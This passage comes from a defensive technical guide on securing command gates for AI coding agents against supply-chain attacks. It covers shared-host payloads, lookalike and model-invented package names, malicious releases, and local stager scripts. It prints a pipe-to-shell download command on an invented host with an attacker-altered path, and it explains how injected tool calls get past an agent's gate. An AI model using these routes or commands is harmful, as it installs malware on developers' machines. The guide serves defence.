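    project:   /home/dev/project
    reason:    company registry lacks these builds
    expires:   2027-03-05
```

The exception lifts only the domain denial. Both packages must still be on the package list, and every other check still applies. An entry for all of example.org, or for every package on the mirror, would remove the same 12 wrong blocks but give an attacker much more to exploit.

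Sometimes the better fix is to change how the gate processes the input. Singh and Srinivasa tried a rule that allowed an upload only if it matched the approved content exactly. The rule stopped both attacks but also rejected two harmless uploads with different formatting. When they converted the content to a standard form before comparing it, the gate allowed both harmless uploads and still stopped both attacks, although this follow-up had only four runs.

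6. Give every exception an expiry date. When the date passes, the gate goes back to denying the command, and someone has to decide whether the project still needs the exception. Without a date, the list only grows, because a missing entry produces complaints and an unnecessary one does not. An approval given during a session should cover only the command that the developer read. NVIDIA rejects the practice of approving an action once and then letting it run many times, at least for actions that would otherwise break the limits on the agent.

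7. Rerun the attack tests after each change, one change at a time. Add new attacks that come close to the exception, such as an unlisted package from mirror.example.org or `numpy` from an unlisted host. If an attack that used to fail now succeeds, withdraw the exception and write a narrower one.

8. Run the 500 commands that were set aside. If the gate blocks none of them, the true rate is probably below 0.6%, as long as the commands are varied enough to count as separate cases. If it blocks many, the exceptions fit the old recordings too closely. The developer should then sort the new blocks by cause and record a fresh set of commands for the next measurement, because the old one has now influenced the rules.

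## When the payload sits on an allowed domain

A domain rule identifies the server a file comes from, but code-hosting sites, cloud storage services and package registries all let strangers upload files under a shared host name. Docker warns in its documentation that allowing a broad domain such as github.com permits access to any content there, including whatever its users upload. The adaptive attacker in Liu and colleagues' benchmark exploited this gap and one other.

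### Two files on one host

Suppose a developer wants a code formatter from a project called acme/formatter. The project is on code.example.org, an invented public code-hosting site that the team has put on its domain list. The project's instructions give one line, which downloads an installation script and passes it straight to a shell:

```
curl -L https://code.example.org/acme/formatter/main/install.sh | bash
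```

`curl` is a download program, `-L` tells it to follow redirects, and `main` is the branch that holds the project's latest code. Assume that the team has added both `curl` and `bash` to its permitted programs so that instructions like this work. A dishonest router can then change the account name in the address:

| | Trusted project | Stranger's copy |
|---|---|---|
| Path in the address | /acme/formatter/main/install.sh | /visitor/formatter/main/install.sh |
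| Operand the gate extracts | code.example.org | code.example.org |
| Verdict | Allow | Allow |

A gate that checks only the domain can't distinguish a payload from a legitimate file on the same domain, because their addresses differ only in the path. Some storage services give each customer a separate subdomain, which the gate can distinguish if it matches hostnames exactly, but not if it allows the whole service with a wildcard.

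Restricting HTTP methods doesn't stop an agent from downloading the payload either. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* describes a setting that limits an agent to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests. This stops most uploads of stolen data, but ordinary downloads use GET and are still allowed.

### Malware on trusted developer hosts

Criminals already use trusted hosts on a large scale. In March 2025, Trend Micro described a campaign that spread password-stealing malware through fake GitHub repositories. *How I found 10,000 GitHub repositories distributing Trojan malware* (Orchid, 2026) begins with a copy of Orchid's own project. The copy had every original commit (a recorded change to the code) and listed Orchid as a contributor. The only difference was an added link to an archive. GitHub took about six weeks to remove the copies Orchid reported.

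Other copies targeted people who work with AI. Help Net Security's *GitHub-hosted malware campaign uses split payload to evade detection* (2026) covers more than 300 malicious packages found by the security firm Netskope, including one that posed as a ready-to-run image of the OpenClaw assistant. Help Net Security's *AI developers targeted via trojanized GitHub repositories* (2026) reports that in August, Netskope found cloned repositories for AI tools in which attackers had hidden malware in a subfolder or changed the addresses in the installation instructions.

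Island's *AgentBaiting* (2026) counted about 7,600 malicious repositories in an operation called FakeGit, with more than 14 million downloads. Over 800 of them posed as skills or MCP servers for agents. IT-Administrator's *Über 17.600 GitHub-Repositories verbreiten Malware* reports that the security firm Apiiro had counted 17,610 FakeGit repositories by October. The two counts probably overlap, so they can't be added together.

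An agent may find such a repository even when no router is involved. The Hacker News (2026) reports that in Island's tests, Claude Code, Gemini and ChatGPT all surfaced malicious FakeGit repositories without being given a link. The model itself could then write the malicious repository's address into the command.

Attackers also take over genuine projects. In May 2026, the Megalodon attack altered 5,561 GitHub repositories in six hours, according to Hackread's *5,561 GitHub Repositories Hit by Megalodon Supply Chain Attack in Six Hours*. From 10 to 12 November, attackers with stolen credentials pushed malicious changes to 8,093 repositories, as iXBT reports in *Атака вышла за пределы GitHub* (2026). Most of these changes altered automated jobs that run on GitHub's servers, but in 771 repositories the attackers added a script that runs when someone installs the package, which can happen on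 a developer's machine.

These reports show that a malicious file may come from a host that most teams would put on their allowlist. They can't establish how often an agent would receive such a file, because none of them tested a policy gate and many of the victims were people who followed a download link.

### What each check receives, and when

A gate that reads a command before it runs has only the address as written. Later checks receive more:

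| Check | When it happens | What it can examine | What it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gate in a hook | Before the command starts | The address in the command | Redirects and the file's contents |
| Network proxy | At each connection | The host name, including after a redirect | The path and the contents, which are encrypted |
| Decrypting proxy | At each request | The full address and the contents | Files that look harmless |
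| Hash check | After the download, before the file runs | The exact contents | Anything the file downloads later |

A network proxy can block a redirect to an unlisted host, which a gate that reads only the command misses. But if code.example.org redirects the `curl` command to another account on the same site, the proxy receives the same host name twice and allows both connections. The simplest fix is to leave `-L` out of the permitted options. The gate then refuses the command, and if it is run again without `-L`, `curl` normally stops at the redirect.

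Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* describes the first two checks in Claude Code. Permission rules check the command's text before it runs, and the sandbox's proxy checks the host name the program requests. The proxy does not decrypt traffic, so a program already running may be able to misstate its destination. Anthropic advises teams that need a stronger guarantee to use their own decrypting proxy.

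The file can also change after someone approves its address, and the approval still covers whatever is there at the time of the download. In one documented case from the November campaign, a malicious file appeared at 14:01 and was gone by 14:05. A developer who checked the project just before and just after those times would have found nothing wrong. In October, the FakeGit attackers changed almost 14,000 repositories in 34 hours, mostly by replacing download links on existing pages.

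### What a list of 205 domains blocked

The August 2026 study *Permission Denied* shows how much a domain list interferes with ordinary work. The researchers ran 12 coding agents on the 89 tasks of Terminal-Bench 2.1, a benchmark of command-line work, three times per task under each of three policies. The strictest policy sent all network traffic through a proxy that allowed only 205 developer domains and the address of the agent's own provider. The researchers adapted the list from Anthropic's default for Claude Code's cloud sessions and added no domains to suit the tasks.

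In the benchmark's own solutions, 36 of the 89 tasks need something from the network. The solutions use 30 domains, and only nine of them were allowed. But the network block alone made only one task impossible. That task needed a specific file from Hugging Face, a site that hosts models and datasets, and no allowed host had a copy. The researchers found an equivalent on an allowed host for every other blocked dependency. For example, when the main archive for the R language was blocked, the same packages were available from another package channel. Six more tasks were impossible because they required writing to folders that the policy had made read-only.

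The remaining 82 tasks had success rates as follows, with all 12 agents combined:

| Policy | Restrictions | Success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Control | None | 72.5% |
| Non-root | No administrator rights | 66.9% |
| Strictest | As above, with the domain list, read-only system folders and tighter limits on privileges | 65.1% |

Most of the drop in success came from removing administrator rights. The last step lowered success by 1.8 percentage points, and the domain list was only one part of that step, so the study does not isolate the list's effect. Across all 89 tasks, the strictest policy lowered success by between 7.1 points (Grok 4.5) and 18.3 points (Claude Sonnet 5), but Grok 4.5's average cost per task rose by 167.3%.

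Agents often found the other routes without help. In one statistics task, the R archive refused their requests in 31 of 36 runs. They then tried one mirror after another until they found the package in an allowed operating-system repository.

The policy remains usable because the allowed hosts hold copies of so many things, but this also gives attackers a lot of room. One of the researchers' solutions took an R package from a mirror on GitHub, and another took a model's weights from GitHub repositories. Anyone who can upload a faithful copy to such a host can also upload an altered one, and the proxy would allow both. The study measured how much the policy reduced performance and did not test how well it stopped attacks like this.

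Allowed hosts differ in who can publish on them. A Linux distribution's maintainers decide what enters its main repository, whereas anyone can open an account on a code-hosting site. A team can therefore keep the curated repositories and apply stricter rules to the open hosts, which narrows the list without losing every substitute.

### Rules on account and path

The easiest way to tighten the rule is to add the account and project to the host. The team replaces its entry for code.example.org with one for `https://code.example.org/acme/formatter/`. The gate then allows the original command and denies the stranger's version.

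GitHub supports such rules in the firewall for its Copilot agent. An entry for a domain covers that host and all its subdomains. An entry for a URL covers only the given protocol, host and path, along with anything beneath that path.

Small errors can make a path rule far too broad. If a gate compares paths as plain text, a rule for `/acme` also matches an account called `/acme-tools`, so the rule needs a final slash. The gate also needs to convert addresses to a standard form before comparing them, as it does with package names. In the rule format that Coder's *Rules engine documentation* describes, a rule can specify a method, a domain and a path, and a missing part matches everything, so forgetting the path opens the whole host. A gate can prevent this by refusing to load any rule that names a shared host without a path.

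A hook can read the URL path in the command, but a network proxy has to decrypt the traffic to see it. GitHub's *Agentic Workflow Firewall* filters by path only when it decrypts traffic. The main drawback of enforcing paths on the network is that the team has to make every program in the sandbox trust the proxy's certificate.

The rule must also cover every host name through which a service delivers files. In Claude Code's cloud sessions, a proxy blocks source archives from GitHub repositories, even public ones, that the user hasn't attached to the session. But Anthropic notes that individual files from public repositories come through a separate domain, which is on the default allowlist, so those files stay reachable.

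The gate should return "deny" rather than "ask" for an unlisted account on a shared host, because a developer who opens that account's page may find the right project name, the full history and the original author's name, as Orchid did.

The remaining attack is to change the trusted project itself. In the November campaign, the attackers tested stolen credentials by opening harmless change requests in 61,764 repositories, according to Help Net Security's *Check your GitHub repos* (2026). Of these requests, 10,431 went to repositories that the stolen account did not own but could reach as a collaborator or through an organization. Trusting acme/formatter therefore means relying on the security of everyone who can write to it.

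### Fixed versions

The address in the example ends in `main/install.sh`, so it returns whatever the project contains at that moment. The team can instead name one commit. Git, the version-control system behind most code-hosting sites, calculates each commit's identifier from the project's contents and history, so any later change has a different identifier. With the identifier shortened, the command becomes:

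```
curl https://code.example.org/acme/formatter/3b9f.../install.sh | bash
```

The rules file has to contain the identifier itself. If it only requires that an address include some identifier, a router can substitute a different one. A label such as `v2.3.1` is easier to read but weaker, because anyone who controls the project can usually move it to a different commit.

A team that had pinned a clean commit in October would have been unaffected by a malicious change that was added and removed in November. However, someone must review and enter each new version, and until they do, the team goes without any security fixes it contains.

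Pinning a version too early can lock in malware. In the November campaign, automated publishing carried the malicious code into a numbered release of a PHP package. Go's module proxy still caches a malicious commit to a Go module, according to *Атака вышла за пределы GitHub*. Waiting a few days before adopting a release would have helped, because the security firm Aikido had exposed the campaign by 12 November.

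Delivery is still a risk because `curl` does not recalculate the commit identifier and accepts whatever the host sends for the requested URL. If an attacker controls the host or a redirect, a correct command can download the wrong file.

### Content hashes

A content hash closes that gap by identifying the file itself. SHA-256, a common hash function, turns a file of any size into 64 hexadecimal digits, and nobody has published a practical way to make a different file with the same result. The team reads `install.sh` once, calculates its hash and stores it with the address:

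```
downloads:
  - address:  https://code.example.org/acme/formatter/3b9f.../install.sh
    sha256:   a41c...
    reviewed: 2026-12-01
```

A hook that runs before the command cannot check the hash, because the file has not arrived yet. The one-line command leaves no later opportunity either, since `bash` starts executing the script while `curl` is still receiving it. The gate therefore needs a small download program of its own, which the agent uses instead of `curl`:

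```
fetch(address):
    entry = downloads[address]       # no entry: error
    file  = download(address)        # into a folder only the gate can write to
    if sha256(file) != entry.sha256:
        delete file
        return DENY
    return file                      # read-only for the agent
```

In the example, the agent receives the script only if it matches the reviewed version byte for byte. If the host, a redirect or a hijacked account supplies anything else, the program deletes it. If the script matches, the agent must run the same read-only file that passed the check, because a copy in the workspace could change before the agent runs it.

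The hash has to come from the team's own review. An attacker who can replace a download can often also replace the hash published beside it. A hash that arrives in the tool call is also unreliable, because a router could have written it.

Hashes also reduce the tension that *Permission Denied* exposed. Several of the researchers' own solutions fetched a substitute from an allowed host and compared it with a known hash. If the hash matches, the team doesn't need to trust whoever uploaded the copy or runs the mirror, so it can accept files from many mirrors.

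Checking files by hash requires one entry for every version of every file, and a harmless update produces a false positive until someone reviews it. The check still misses a file that was already malicious when the team hashed it, and a second file that the script downloads while running. Installation scripts often download the actual program this way, so the reviewer should look for such downloads and either give each one its own hash or store the finished program instead of the script.

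### An internal mirror

With a mirror, the team keeps approved files on its own server and removes the public host from the domain list. The agent's command now fetches `https://files.example.com/formatter/2.3.1/install.sh`, and the gate denies any address on code.example.org. If a network proxy enforces the same list, a second download from inside the script also fails unless the mirror holds that file. A hash on the script alone could not prevent that download.

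Existing products need some adjustment to work this way. In Claude Code's cloud sessions, a user can clear the "Allow package managers" box, which removes the default domains, and then list only the mirror. GitHub traffic still goes through its own proxy, and the list doesn't apply to it. The firewall for GitHub's Copilot agent covers only processes that the agent starts through its Bash tool, so MCP servers and setup steps can still reach other hosts.

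The mirror must not copy new files automatically. In July 2026, attackers altered the repositories behind ten PHP packages, and the public registry Packagist picked up the malicious development versions without anyone approving them, according to The Hacker News' *Attackers Weaponize GitHub Actions Runners to Target cPanel and WHM Servers* (2026). Those files ran on GitHub's servers, not on the machines of people who installed the packages, but the same automatic copying would also have delivered an installation script.

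Someone has to approve each file on the mirror, run the server and delete files that later turn out to be malicious. A mirror therefore takes more work than the other fixes, and it suits teams that share many downloads. A team with a dozen downloads can get most of the benefit from hashes. An attacker who gets a malicious file past the reviewer reaches every developer who uses the mirror, so the mirror's upload rights need at least as much protection as the gate's own rules.

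### A ban on running remote scripts directly

The last repair is easy to add and works with any of the others. The gate denies every command that passes a download directly into a shell or another interpreter, regardless of the address. In the example, it refuses the line even when the account, commit and host are all correct. The refusal message includes an instruction to use the download program instead, which leaves time to check the hash before anything runs.

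The safest way to write the ban is to permit downloads only through that program. Claude Code users can add `curl` to the deny list, but Anthropic warns that such a rule matches the command as written, and recommends the sandbox for enforcement that doesn't depend on the command's text. Without the sandbox, a script or another program could still make the same connection.

The ban does not inspect the file, so it stops very little by itself. A router can send the download and the execution as two separate commands, and the second command then refers only to a file on the developer's disk.

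## Checking what a package install will bring in

A package registry is another shared host, but a gate has less to check in an install command than in a download. The install command contains only a package name, and the installer determines which files to fetch for it.

### The stages of an install

The command from the earlier examples names one package:

```
pip install --index-url https://packages.example.com/simple requests
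```

On a clean machine pip installs five, because `requests` depends on `certifi`, `charset-normalizer`, `idna` and `urllib3`.

| Stage | What the installer does | What a gate can check |
|---|---|---|
| Resolve the name | Looks up `requests` on the registry | The registry and the name, as written |
| Choose a version | Takes the newest release that fits | The version, if the command names one |
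| Resolve dependencies | Reads what `requests` needs, then what those packages need | Nothing in the command's text |
| Fetch | Downloads an archive for each package | The hash of each archive |
| Install | Unpacks the archives and, for some packages, runs code from them | Whether the settings let package code run |

The gate can check more than the command's text by first having the installer list what it would install. With the options `--dry-run` and `--report`, pip lists every package it would install, with versions and hashes, without installing them. If a package comes only as source code, pip may run the package's own build code to find out what it depends on, so the check itself could run malware. Adding `--only-binary :all:` prevents this by limiting pip to wheels, which are ready-built packages that pip only unpacks. For JavaScript, `npm install --package-lock-only` writes the full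 list to a file without installing anything.

### One swapped pair of letters

In dependency substitution, the router changes `requests` to `reqeusts`, a lookalike that the attacker has already published on PyPI. The company registry, packages.example.com, mirrors PyPI, so it offers the lookalike too, and a domain rule allows the command. A hash supplied by the registry doesn't detect the substitution, because it matches the lookalike's file.

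A list of approved package names, matched exactly, catches the misspelling `reqeusts` because that name is not on the list. This check doesn't depend on whether the package is malicious or how long it has existed. A list of known bad names would never be complete, since developers create 700 to 800 new projects on PyPI every day, according to PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026).

Some tools look for suspicious spellings instead. They often use the Levenshtein distance, which is the smallest number of single-letter insertions, deletions and substitutions needed to turn one word into another.

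```
requests    r e q u e s t s
reqeusts    r e q e u s t s
                  ^ ^
```

The two names differ only in the fourth and fifth letters, where `u` and `e` are swapped. Their Levenshtein distance is 2, because a single substitution would correct only one of the letters and a single insertion or deletion would change the length. Their Damerau–Levenshtein distance is 1, because that measure also counts a swap of neighbouring letters as one edit. A tool that flags only names one edit away will miss this lookalike if it uses Levenshtein distance.

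With the limit raised to two edits, a match means little because many honest packages have similar names, such as `boto` and `boto3`, both from Amazon, or `react` and `preact`. Registries are also crowded, with about 857,000 names on PyPI and 4.2 million on npm. *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (Churilov, 2026) found that 81 of 104 names made up by language models were within two edits of a real package.

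*ConfuGuard* (Jiang, Çakar and colleagues, 2025) examined a sample of packages that an earlier detector had flagged for their names but malware scans had not. The researchers judged 464 of 601 (77.2%) to be benign and suspected that the rest were intended for later attacks. Checking other information, such as whether a package had a purpose of its own, cut their false-positive rate from 77% to 13%. *AgentGuard* (Li, Ma and colleagues, 2026) reports a smaller reduction for the same tool, from 80% to 28%. Since this work concerns packages with suspicious names, neither result can be used to predict how often such a check would interrupt ordinary installs.

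Spelling distance is therefore more useful for choosing which similar name to show in the approval prompt than for deciding the gate's verdict.

### A malicious release of an approved package

On 24 March 2026, attackers uploaded versions 1.82.7 and 1.82.8 of LiteLLM to PyPI. PyPI traces the attack to an access token exposed through Trivy, a security scanner the project used. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), the attackers bypassed the project's release process, and the source code on GitHub stayed clean. An allowlist of package names that included `litellm` would have allowed `pip install litellm`, and pip would have installed the newest version.

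LiteLLM versions 1.82.7 and 1.82.8 both contained code that stole passwords and keys. In 1.82.7, the code ran when a program imported the affected part of LiteLLM. Version 1.82.8 added a `.pth` file, a type that Python processes every time it starts, so installing that version was enough for the code to run, even if no program imported LiteLLM (Willison, 2026, *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8*).

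PyPI received the first report 1 hour 19 minutes after the upload and quarantined the project after 2 hours 32 minutes. PyPI counted more than 119,000 downloads of the malicious versions. LiteLLM says the exposure lasted about 40 minutes, and Daniel Hnyk found 46,996 downloads in 46 minutes (relayed in Willison, 2026). The accounts don't explain the difference, but in all of them the exposure lasted well under a day.

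PyPI also estimated that 40% to 50% of LiteLLM installs were for the newest version. LiteLLM normally has about 1,700 installs a minute, or roughly 258,000 in 152 minutes. The 119,000 malicious downloads are 46% of that, which is within PyPI's range. The other installs presumably specified an older version and so avoided the malware.

The fix is to treat the version as another operand. The gate allows `litellm==1.82.6` if the rules file lists that version, and refuses `litellm` without a version. As with commit identifiers, the rules have to include the exact version number.

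### A dependency that the command doesn't name

A week later, attackers published two malicious versions of Axios, a JavaScript library with 101 million downloads a week. Willison notes that both versions added a dependency, `plain-crypto-js`, which contained the malware. The command `npm install axios` does not include that name, so a gate that reads only the command cannot check the dependency against its list.

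LiteLLM also reached people this way. Hnyk found 2,337 packages that depended on it, 88% of which would have accepted the malicious releases. A developer who installed one of these packages could have received LiteLLM without having heard of it. Specifying an exact version of the package in the command doesn't necessarily help, because that package may still accept any recent version of its own dependencies.

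The gate therefore has to apply its rules to every package in the installer's plan. An allowlist of exact package names would then have stopped `plain-crypto-js`, but it would also have to include every legitimate dependency, which means five entries for `requests` instead of one and often hundreds for a JavaScript project. Few teams will maintain such a list by hand, so it makes sense to generate it from the project's lockfile (described below).

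### A name that a model invented

Language models sometimes recommend packages that don't exist. If an attacker registers one of those names, the model's next command to install that package will download the attacker's code. The attack requires neither a router nor a typing error. Security researchers call this slopsquatting.

Churilov gave each of five models from late 2025 and early 2026 about 40,000 programming questions on Python and JavaScript. Between 3.6% (Claude Haiku 4.5) and 5.0% (GPT-5.4-mini) of the packages they mentioned did not exist when the model answered. All five models had 104 invented names in common, so an attacker who registered one of them could reach users of several providers. The models could not look packages up, and an agent that checks the registry first might do better.

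Small models that people run on their own machines can be much worse. In *Secure or Suspect?*, Haque, Lin and colleagues (2025) asked Qwen models for commands that install Go packages. For questions from Stack Overflow, the smallest model invented 40.6% of the packages. On another set of tasks, its rate of invented packages rose from 53.6% to 98.8% when the researchers compressed the model to 4-bit precision.

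Few people seem to be registering these invented names so far. Of 2,282 that Churilov tracked, 25 (1.1%) appeared on a registry within about six months. At least one contained malware, and researchers may have reserved others. If attackers registered names without regard to how often models produce them, between 1 in 1,800 and 1 in 2,500 package mentions would be of a name they had registered. A deliberate attacker would choose the names that models produce most often and reach more people. At least 23 other names that the models suggested had hosted malware, which the registries had since removed.

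Aikido found an invented package name, `react-codeshift`, that had spread without anyone deliberately promoting it. It blends the names of two real packages, `jscodeshift` and `react-codemod`, and first appeared in a set of 47 agent skills written by a language model. An Aikido researcher registered the name in January 2026 to keep attackers from taking it, and by then agents were already trying to use it.

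A name list blocks an invented package at first, but people may later add it to the list. When the gate prompts for approval of the new name, the developer may look it up, find that the package exists and approve it. Or the model may write the name into the project's manifest and a reviewer may accept the change, after which the exception for declared packages allows every install of that package.

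Checking that a package name exists is weak protection. Raj and Sahu (2026), in *Names Can Hurt*, built a detector for invented names and tested it mainly on a small Llama model. About half of its 179 warnings were for packages that already existed on PyPI, so an existence check would have missed them. These packages were not necessarily malicious. The most common was `pil`, with 36 warnings. Python programs use that name for the image library Pillow, so an agent that installs the name it sees in the code gets a different package, or none.

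The approval prompt should therefore show more than whether a package exists. Raj and Sahu's detector relied mostly on the number of maintainers and on whether the package linked to a GitHub project, but an attacker can add such a link. Li and colleagues consider the creation date much harder to forge. A month-old package with only one release deserves suspicion if the model presents it as a standard tool.

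### What each repair stops

Five repairs address these attacks, and none covers all of them.

| Repair | Lookalike or invented name | Malicious release | Malicious indirect dependency |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lockfile with hashes | Stops it unless someone adds the name | Stops it unless someone locks that release | As for a release |
| Private index of approved packages | Stops it unless someone approves it | Stops it unless someone approves it | Stops it unless someone approves it |
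| Waiting period | Stops it only while it is new | Stops it if someone finds the malware in time | As for a release |
| Install scripts off | Stops only code that runs during installation | The same | The same |
| Publisher attestation | Does not stop it | Stops an upload made outside the usual build | Stops it only if the gate expects a certain publisher |

#### Lockfiles with hashes

A lockfile records the exact version and hash of every package in a project, including indirect dependencies. PyPI warns that the output of `pip freeze` isn't a lockfile, because it lists versions without hashes. The hash matters because the files published under a version number can change. Until July 2026, an attacker with a stolen token could have added a new file to an old release on PyPI. PyPI knew of no such attack, but it now rejects new files for releases more than 14 days old.

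The gate can deny all install commands except those that install from the lockfile, such as `npm ci` or pip with `--require-hashes`. Those commands contain no package name for a router to replace. As with the manifest, the gate should use the last version of the lockfile that a person reviewed.

Of the five repairs, lockfiles are the best supported by evidence. Roughly half of all LiteLLM installs during the attack avoided the malware because they didn't take the newest version. The project's official Docker image also used fixed versions, and its users were unaffected. However, an agent can't try a new library or get a security fix until someone updates the lockfile. A team that generated its lockfile during the two and a half hours of the attack would also have locked in the malware.

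#### Private indexes

A private index that holds only approved packages doesn't contain `reqeusts`, so the package can't be installed from there. This also protects installs inside scripts, as long as the machine can't reach any other registry. A mirror that copies everything from PyPI, like the one in the example, doesn't provide this protection.

When a company uses a private package index beside a public one, an attacker can publish a public package under the name of an internal one, and the installer may silently take the public version. The researcher Alex Birsan demonstrated this in 2021. It can happen with pip when a command adds a second index with `--extra-index-url`. A gate should refuse that option, and the pseudocode given earlier does so because its rules don't list it.

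As with a download mirror, the main drawback is having to approve each update. The argument for private indexes is based on how installers choose packages, not on a measured effect like the one for fixed versions.

#### Waiting periods

A waiting period makes the installer ignore releases less than, say, three days old, which gives others time to find any malware. LiteLLM's malicious versions were available for under three hours. Datadog Security Labs judges that even a one-day wait would have blocked the malicious Axios versions.

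GitHub's update service, Dependabot, has waited three days by default since July 2026. GitHub's *The case for a cooldown* supports this with a review of 21 well-known attacks, most of which a wait could have filtered out. The review appears to be the survey in *Minimum Release Age is an Underrated Supply Chain Defense*, which says the survey is not a controlled study. An attack counted as blocked if the registry removed the release within seven days, so the survey supports a seven-day wait more directly than a three-day one.

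The Dependabot default doesn't affect an agent that runs `pip install` itself. To cover that case, the developer has to set the wait in the installer, which pip, uv and npm have all allowed since early 2026 or before. A command-line option can set pip's wait to zero for a single install, so the gate must refuse that option when an agent uses it.

The setting is also easy to get wrong. Tanaka, Tsuchida and colleagues (2026), in *An Exploratory Study of Dependabot Cooldown Adoption in Open-Source GitHub Projects*, found that 135 of 1,462 popular projects had adopted a wait by the end of April 2026, usually of seven days. Another project's file appeared to set a four-day wait but set none, because it used `default` where Dependabot expected `default-days`. The study did not measure how many attacks the waits stopped.

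The main objection to waiting is that it also delays fixes. *On dependency cooldowns* (2025) argues that users often need security fixes promptly, and casts doubt on how well waiting works. Dependabot exempts security updates from its cooldown, according to GitHub's *Dependabot version updates introduce default package cooldown* (2026). A plain `pip install` has no such exemption, so the developer needs a way to approve an urgent fix by hand.

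A waiting period also relies on someone else finding the problem before it ends. Thirteen users reported the LiteLLM malware to PyPI. If everyone waited, fewer users would run into malware early, and detection would depend more on the researchers who scan new uploads. GitHub acknowledges that waiting does little against a backdoor that stays dormant longer than the waiting period.

The gate should measure the waiting period from when each release was uploaded, not from when the package was first published. Jiang and colleagues studied 240 confirmed attacks on npm that used confusing names. In 32 of them (13.3%), the attacker added the malware five or more days after first publishing the package.

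#### Install scripts

npm packages can include scripts that run during installation, and attackers use them to steal credentials before anyone uses the package. Version 12 of npm, released in July 2026, blocks these scripts unless the project allows them. It also blocks dependencies that come from Git repositories or other web addresses instead of the registry. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) explains that a Git dependency could run code even with scripts turned off.

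Packages that compile part of their code during installation stop working until the developer approves them. npm stores these approvals in the project's `package.json` file, which an agent can normally edit. The gate should therefore treat changing those approvals or running `npm approve-scripts` as a request for new permissions.

For pip, the closest equivalent to turning scripts off is restricting installs to wheels. This would not have stopped either LiteLLM release, because their malware ran when Python started or when a program imported the package. Turning scripts off removes the fastest way to run malicious code but leaves the code on the machine.

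#### Publisher attestations

An attestation is a signed statement that links a package file to the source code and the automated build that produced it. Requiring one exposes a release that an attacker uploads directly with a stolen token, as one did with LiteLLM. However, LiteLLM adopted Trusted Publishers, the PyPI feature that creates attestations, only after the attack, so in March a gate that required attestations would have refused the good versions too.

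A gate can't practically require an attestation for every package, because many packages lack them. In late 2024, about 20,000 PyPI packages, a small share of the registry, could produce attestations by default. A gate can instead require one only for packages whose earlier releases had one. For the rest, Willison suggests checking for a matching release on GitHub, which is a weaker signal but was missing for both the LiteLLM and Axios malware.

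An attacker can get a valid attestation for malicious code by taking over a project's build system or by publishing a lookalike package from their own project. The rules file should therefore record which source project each package must come from.

### A rule for the whole plan

A gate can combine the lockfile, the waiting period and the approval prompt in a few lines:

```
check_install(command):
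    plan = resolve(command)        # runs no package code; failure: error
    return strictest(judge_file(f) for f in plan)

judge_file(f):
    if f.hash in reviewed_lockfile:           return ALLOW
    if f.uploaded less than 3 days ago:       return DENY
    return ASK
```

The cases in this section would then turn out as follows:

| What the plan contains | Verdict |
|---|---|
| `requests` and its four dependencies, all in the lockfile | Allow |
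| LiteLLM 1.82.8, one hour after its upload | Deny |
| A new Axios release with a dependency published the same day | Deny |
| `reqeusts`, published a year ago | Ask, with `requests` shown beside it |
| An invented name that someone registered in the spring | Ask, with the package's age and source project |

The last two verdicts depend on a person, and developers often approve prompts without close review. A team that rarely adds packages can replace "ask" with "deny" and have developers update the lockfile themselves. Either way, the gate must install exactly the files in the plan. If it runs the original command again, that command may fetch a newer release than the one the gate checked.

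## When the command runs a script already on disk

An attacker can arrange for a file to reach a developer's disk in one step and run in a later one. The command that runs this file, called a local stager, contains no domain or package name for a gate to check. Liu and colleagues' adaptive attacker used local stagers to get past a gate that had stopped every straightforward injection.

### Two steps that each satisfy the rules

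Suppose a team lets its agent write files in the workspace and run the project's own scripts. A dishonest router can then send two tool calls:

| Time | Tool call | What the gate extracts | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10:02 | Create the file `tools/prepare.sh` | A path inside the workspace | Allow |
| 10:40 | `bash tools/prepare.sh` | A path inside the workspace | Allow |

Both verdicts follow the rules. The harm is in the file's contents. The path rule doesn't check them in the first call, and the second call doesn't include them. A gate that judges each call separately also has no record of the first call when it judges the second. The file could instead come from a download, an archive or a package, and the command that runs it could come days later.

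Ordinary development also works this way. An agent that fixes a bug usually writes a test and then runs it with `pytest`, which executes whatever the test files contain. `make` runs the commands in the project's makefile, and `npm test` runs whatever test command the project's `package.json` defines. A ban on running local files would stop an agent from testing its own work.

A command that runs a script on disk can do more than its text suggests, even without an attacker. In *Approval Laundering*, Wang (2026) gave Claude Code permission to run one exact commit command in a repository with a Git hook, a script that Git runs automatically. The hook added every changed file to the commit. In 9 of 20 runs (45%), the commit included an edit that the permission didn't cover. Wang built the repository to produce this result, so the figure is not a rate for ordinary projects.

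Standing permissions make it easier to run a script already on disk. When a user switches to auto mode, Claude Code drops rules that allow any Python or Node program, or any package-manager `run` command, because those rules let arbitrary code run. Anthropic acknowledges that its list of such rules will always be incomplete. Auto mode also allows file edits inside the project, so the first chance to stop a local stager may come when a command runs it.

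### Letting the gate read the script

Jing's trial of 65 shell scripts (57 attacks and eight harmless) also tested a setup in which the program running the scripts could have a gate read each one first. In the table, an escape is an attack script whose forbidden effect showed up in the comparison of the machine's files.

| What was refused | Escapes, of 57 attack scripts | Harmless scripts blocked, of 8 |
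|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 25 | 0 |
| Scripts with a deny verdict | 0 | 0 |
| Scripts with a deny or ask verdict | 0 | 8 |
| The same, with template lines removed first | 0 | 0 |
| File access outside an AppArmor profile, with no gate | 8 | 0 |

With the gate in place, all 57 attack scripts were refused, and the number of escapes fell from 25 to zero. The gate needed each script's text to do this, because a command like `bash payload.sh` contains only a path. Jing argues that any block based on the path alone would be fake. The program therefore opened each script and passed its contents to the gate. It also passed the folder the shell would start in, because a relative path can point to different files depending on the starting folder.

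When the policy also blocked ask verdicts, it at first stopped all eight harmless scripts. The gate had returned ask 532 times across the 65 scripts, never for a command that did the script's real work. Comment lines accounted for 354 of these verdicts, and lines that the script generator had wrapped around each command accounted for the other 178. These lines probably drew ask verdicts because they name no target, and Jing's gate refers actions without a target to a person. Once Jing removed this template text before the gate read the scripts, the stricter policy blocked the same 57 scripts and none of the harmless ones.

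A gate can likewise remove comments before judging a script, but it must identify them exactly as bash does. Roo Code's parser misidentified comments and ignored text that bash then executed.

AppArmor, a Linux feature that restricts which files a program can use, did less well with the same policy. Eight of the 25 escapes still happened, partly because permission to write in a folder includes permission to destroy what is in it.

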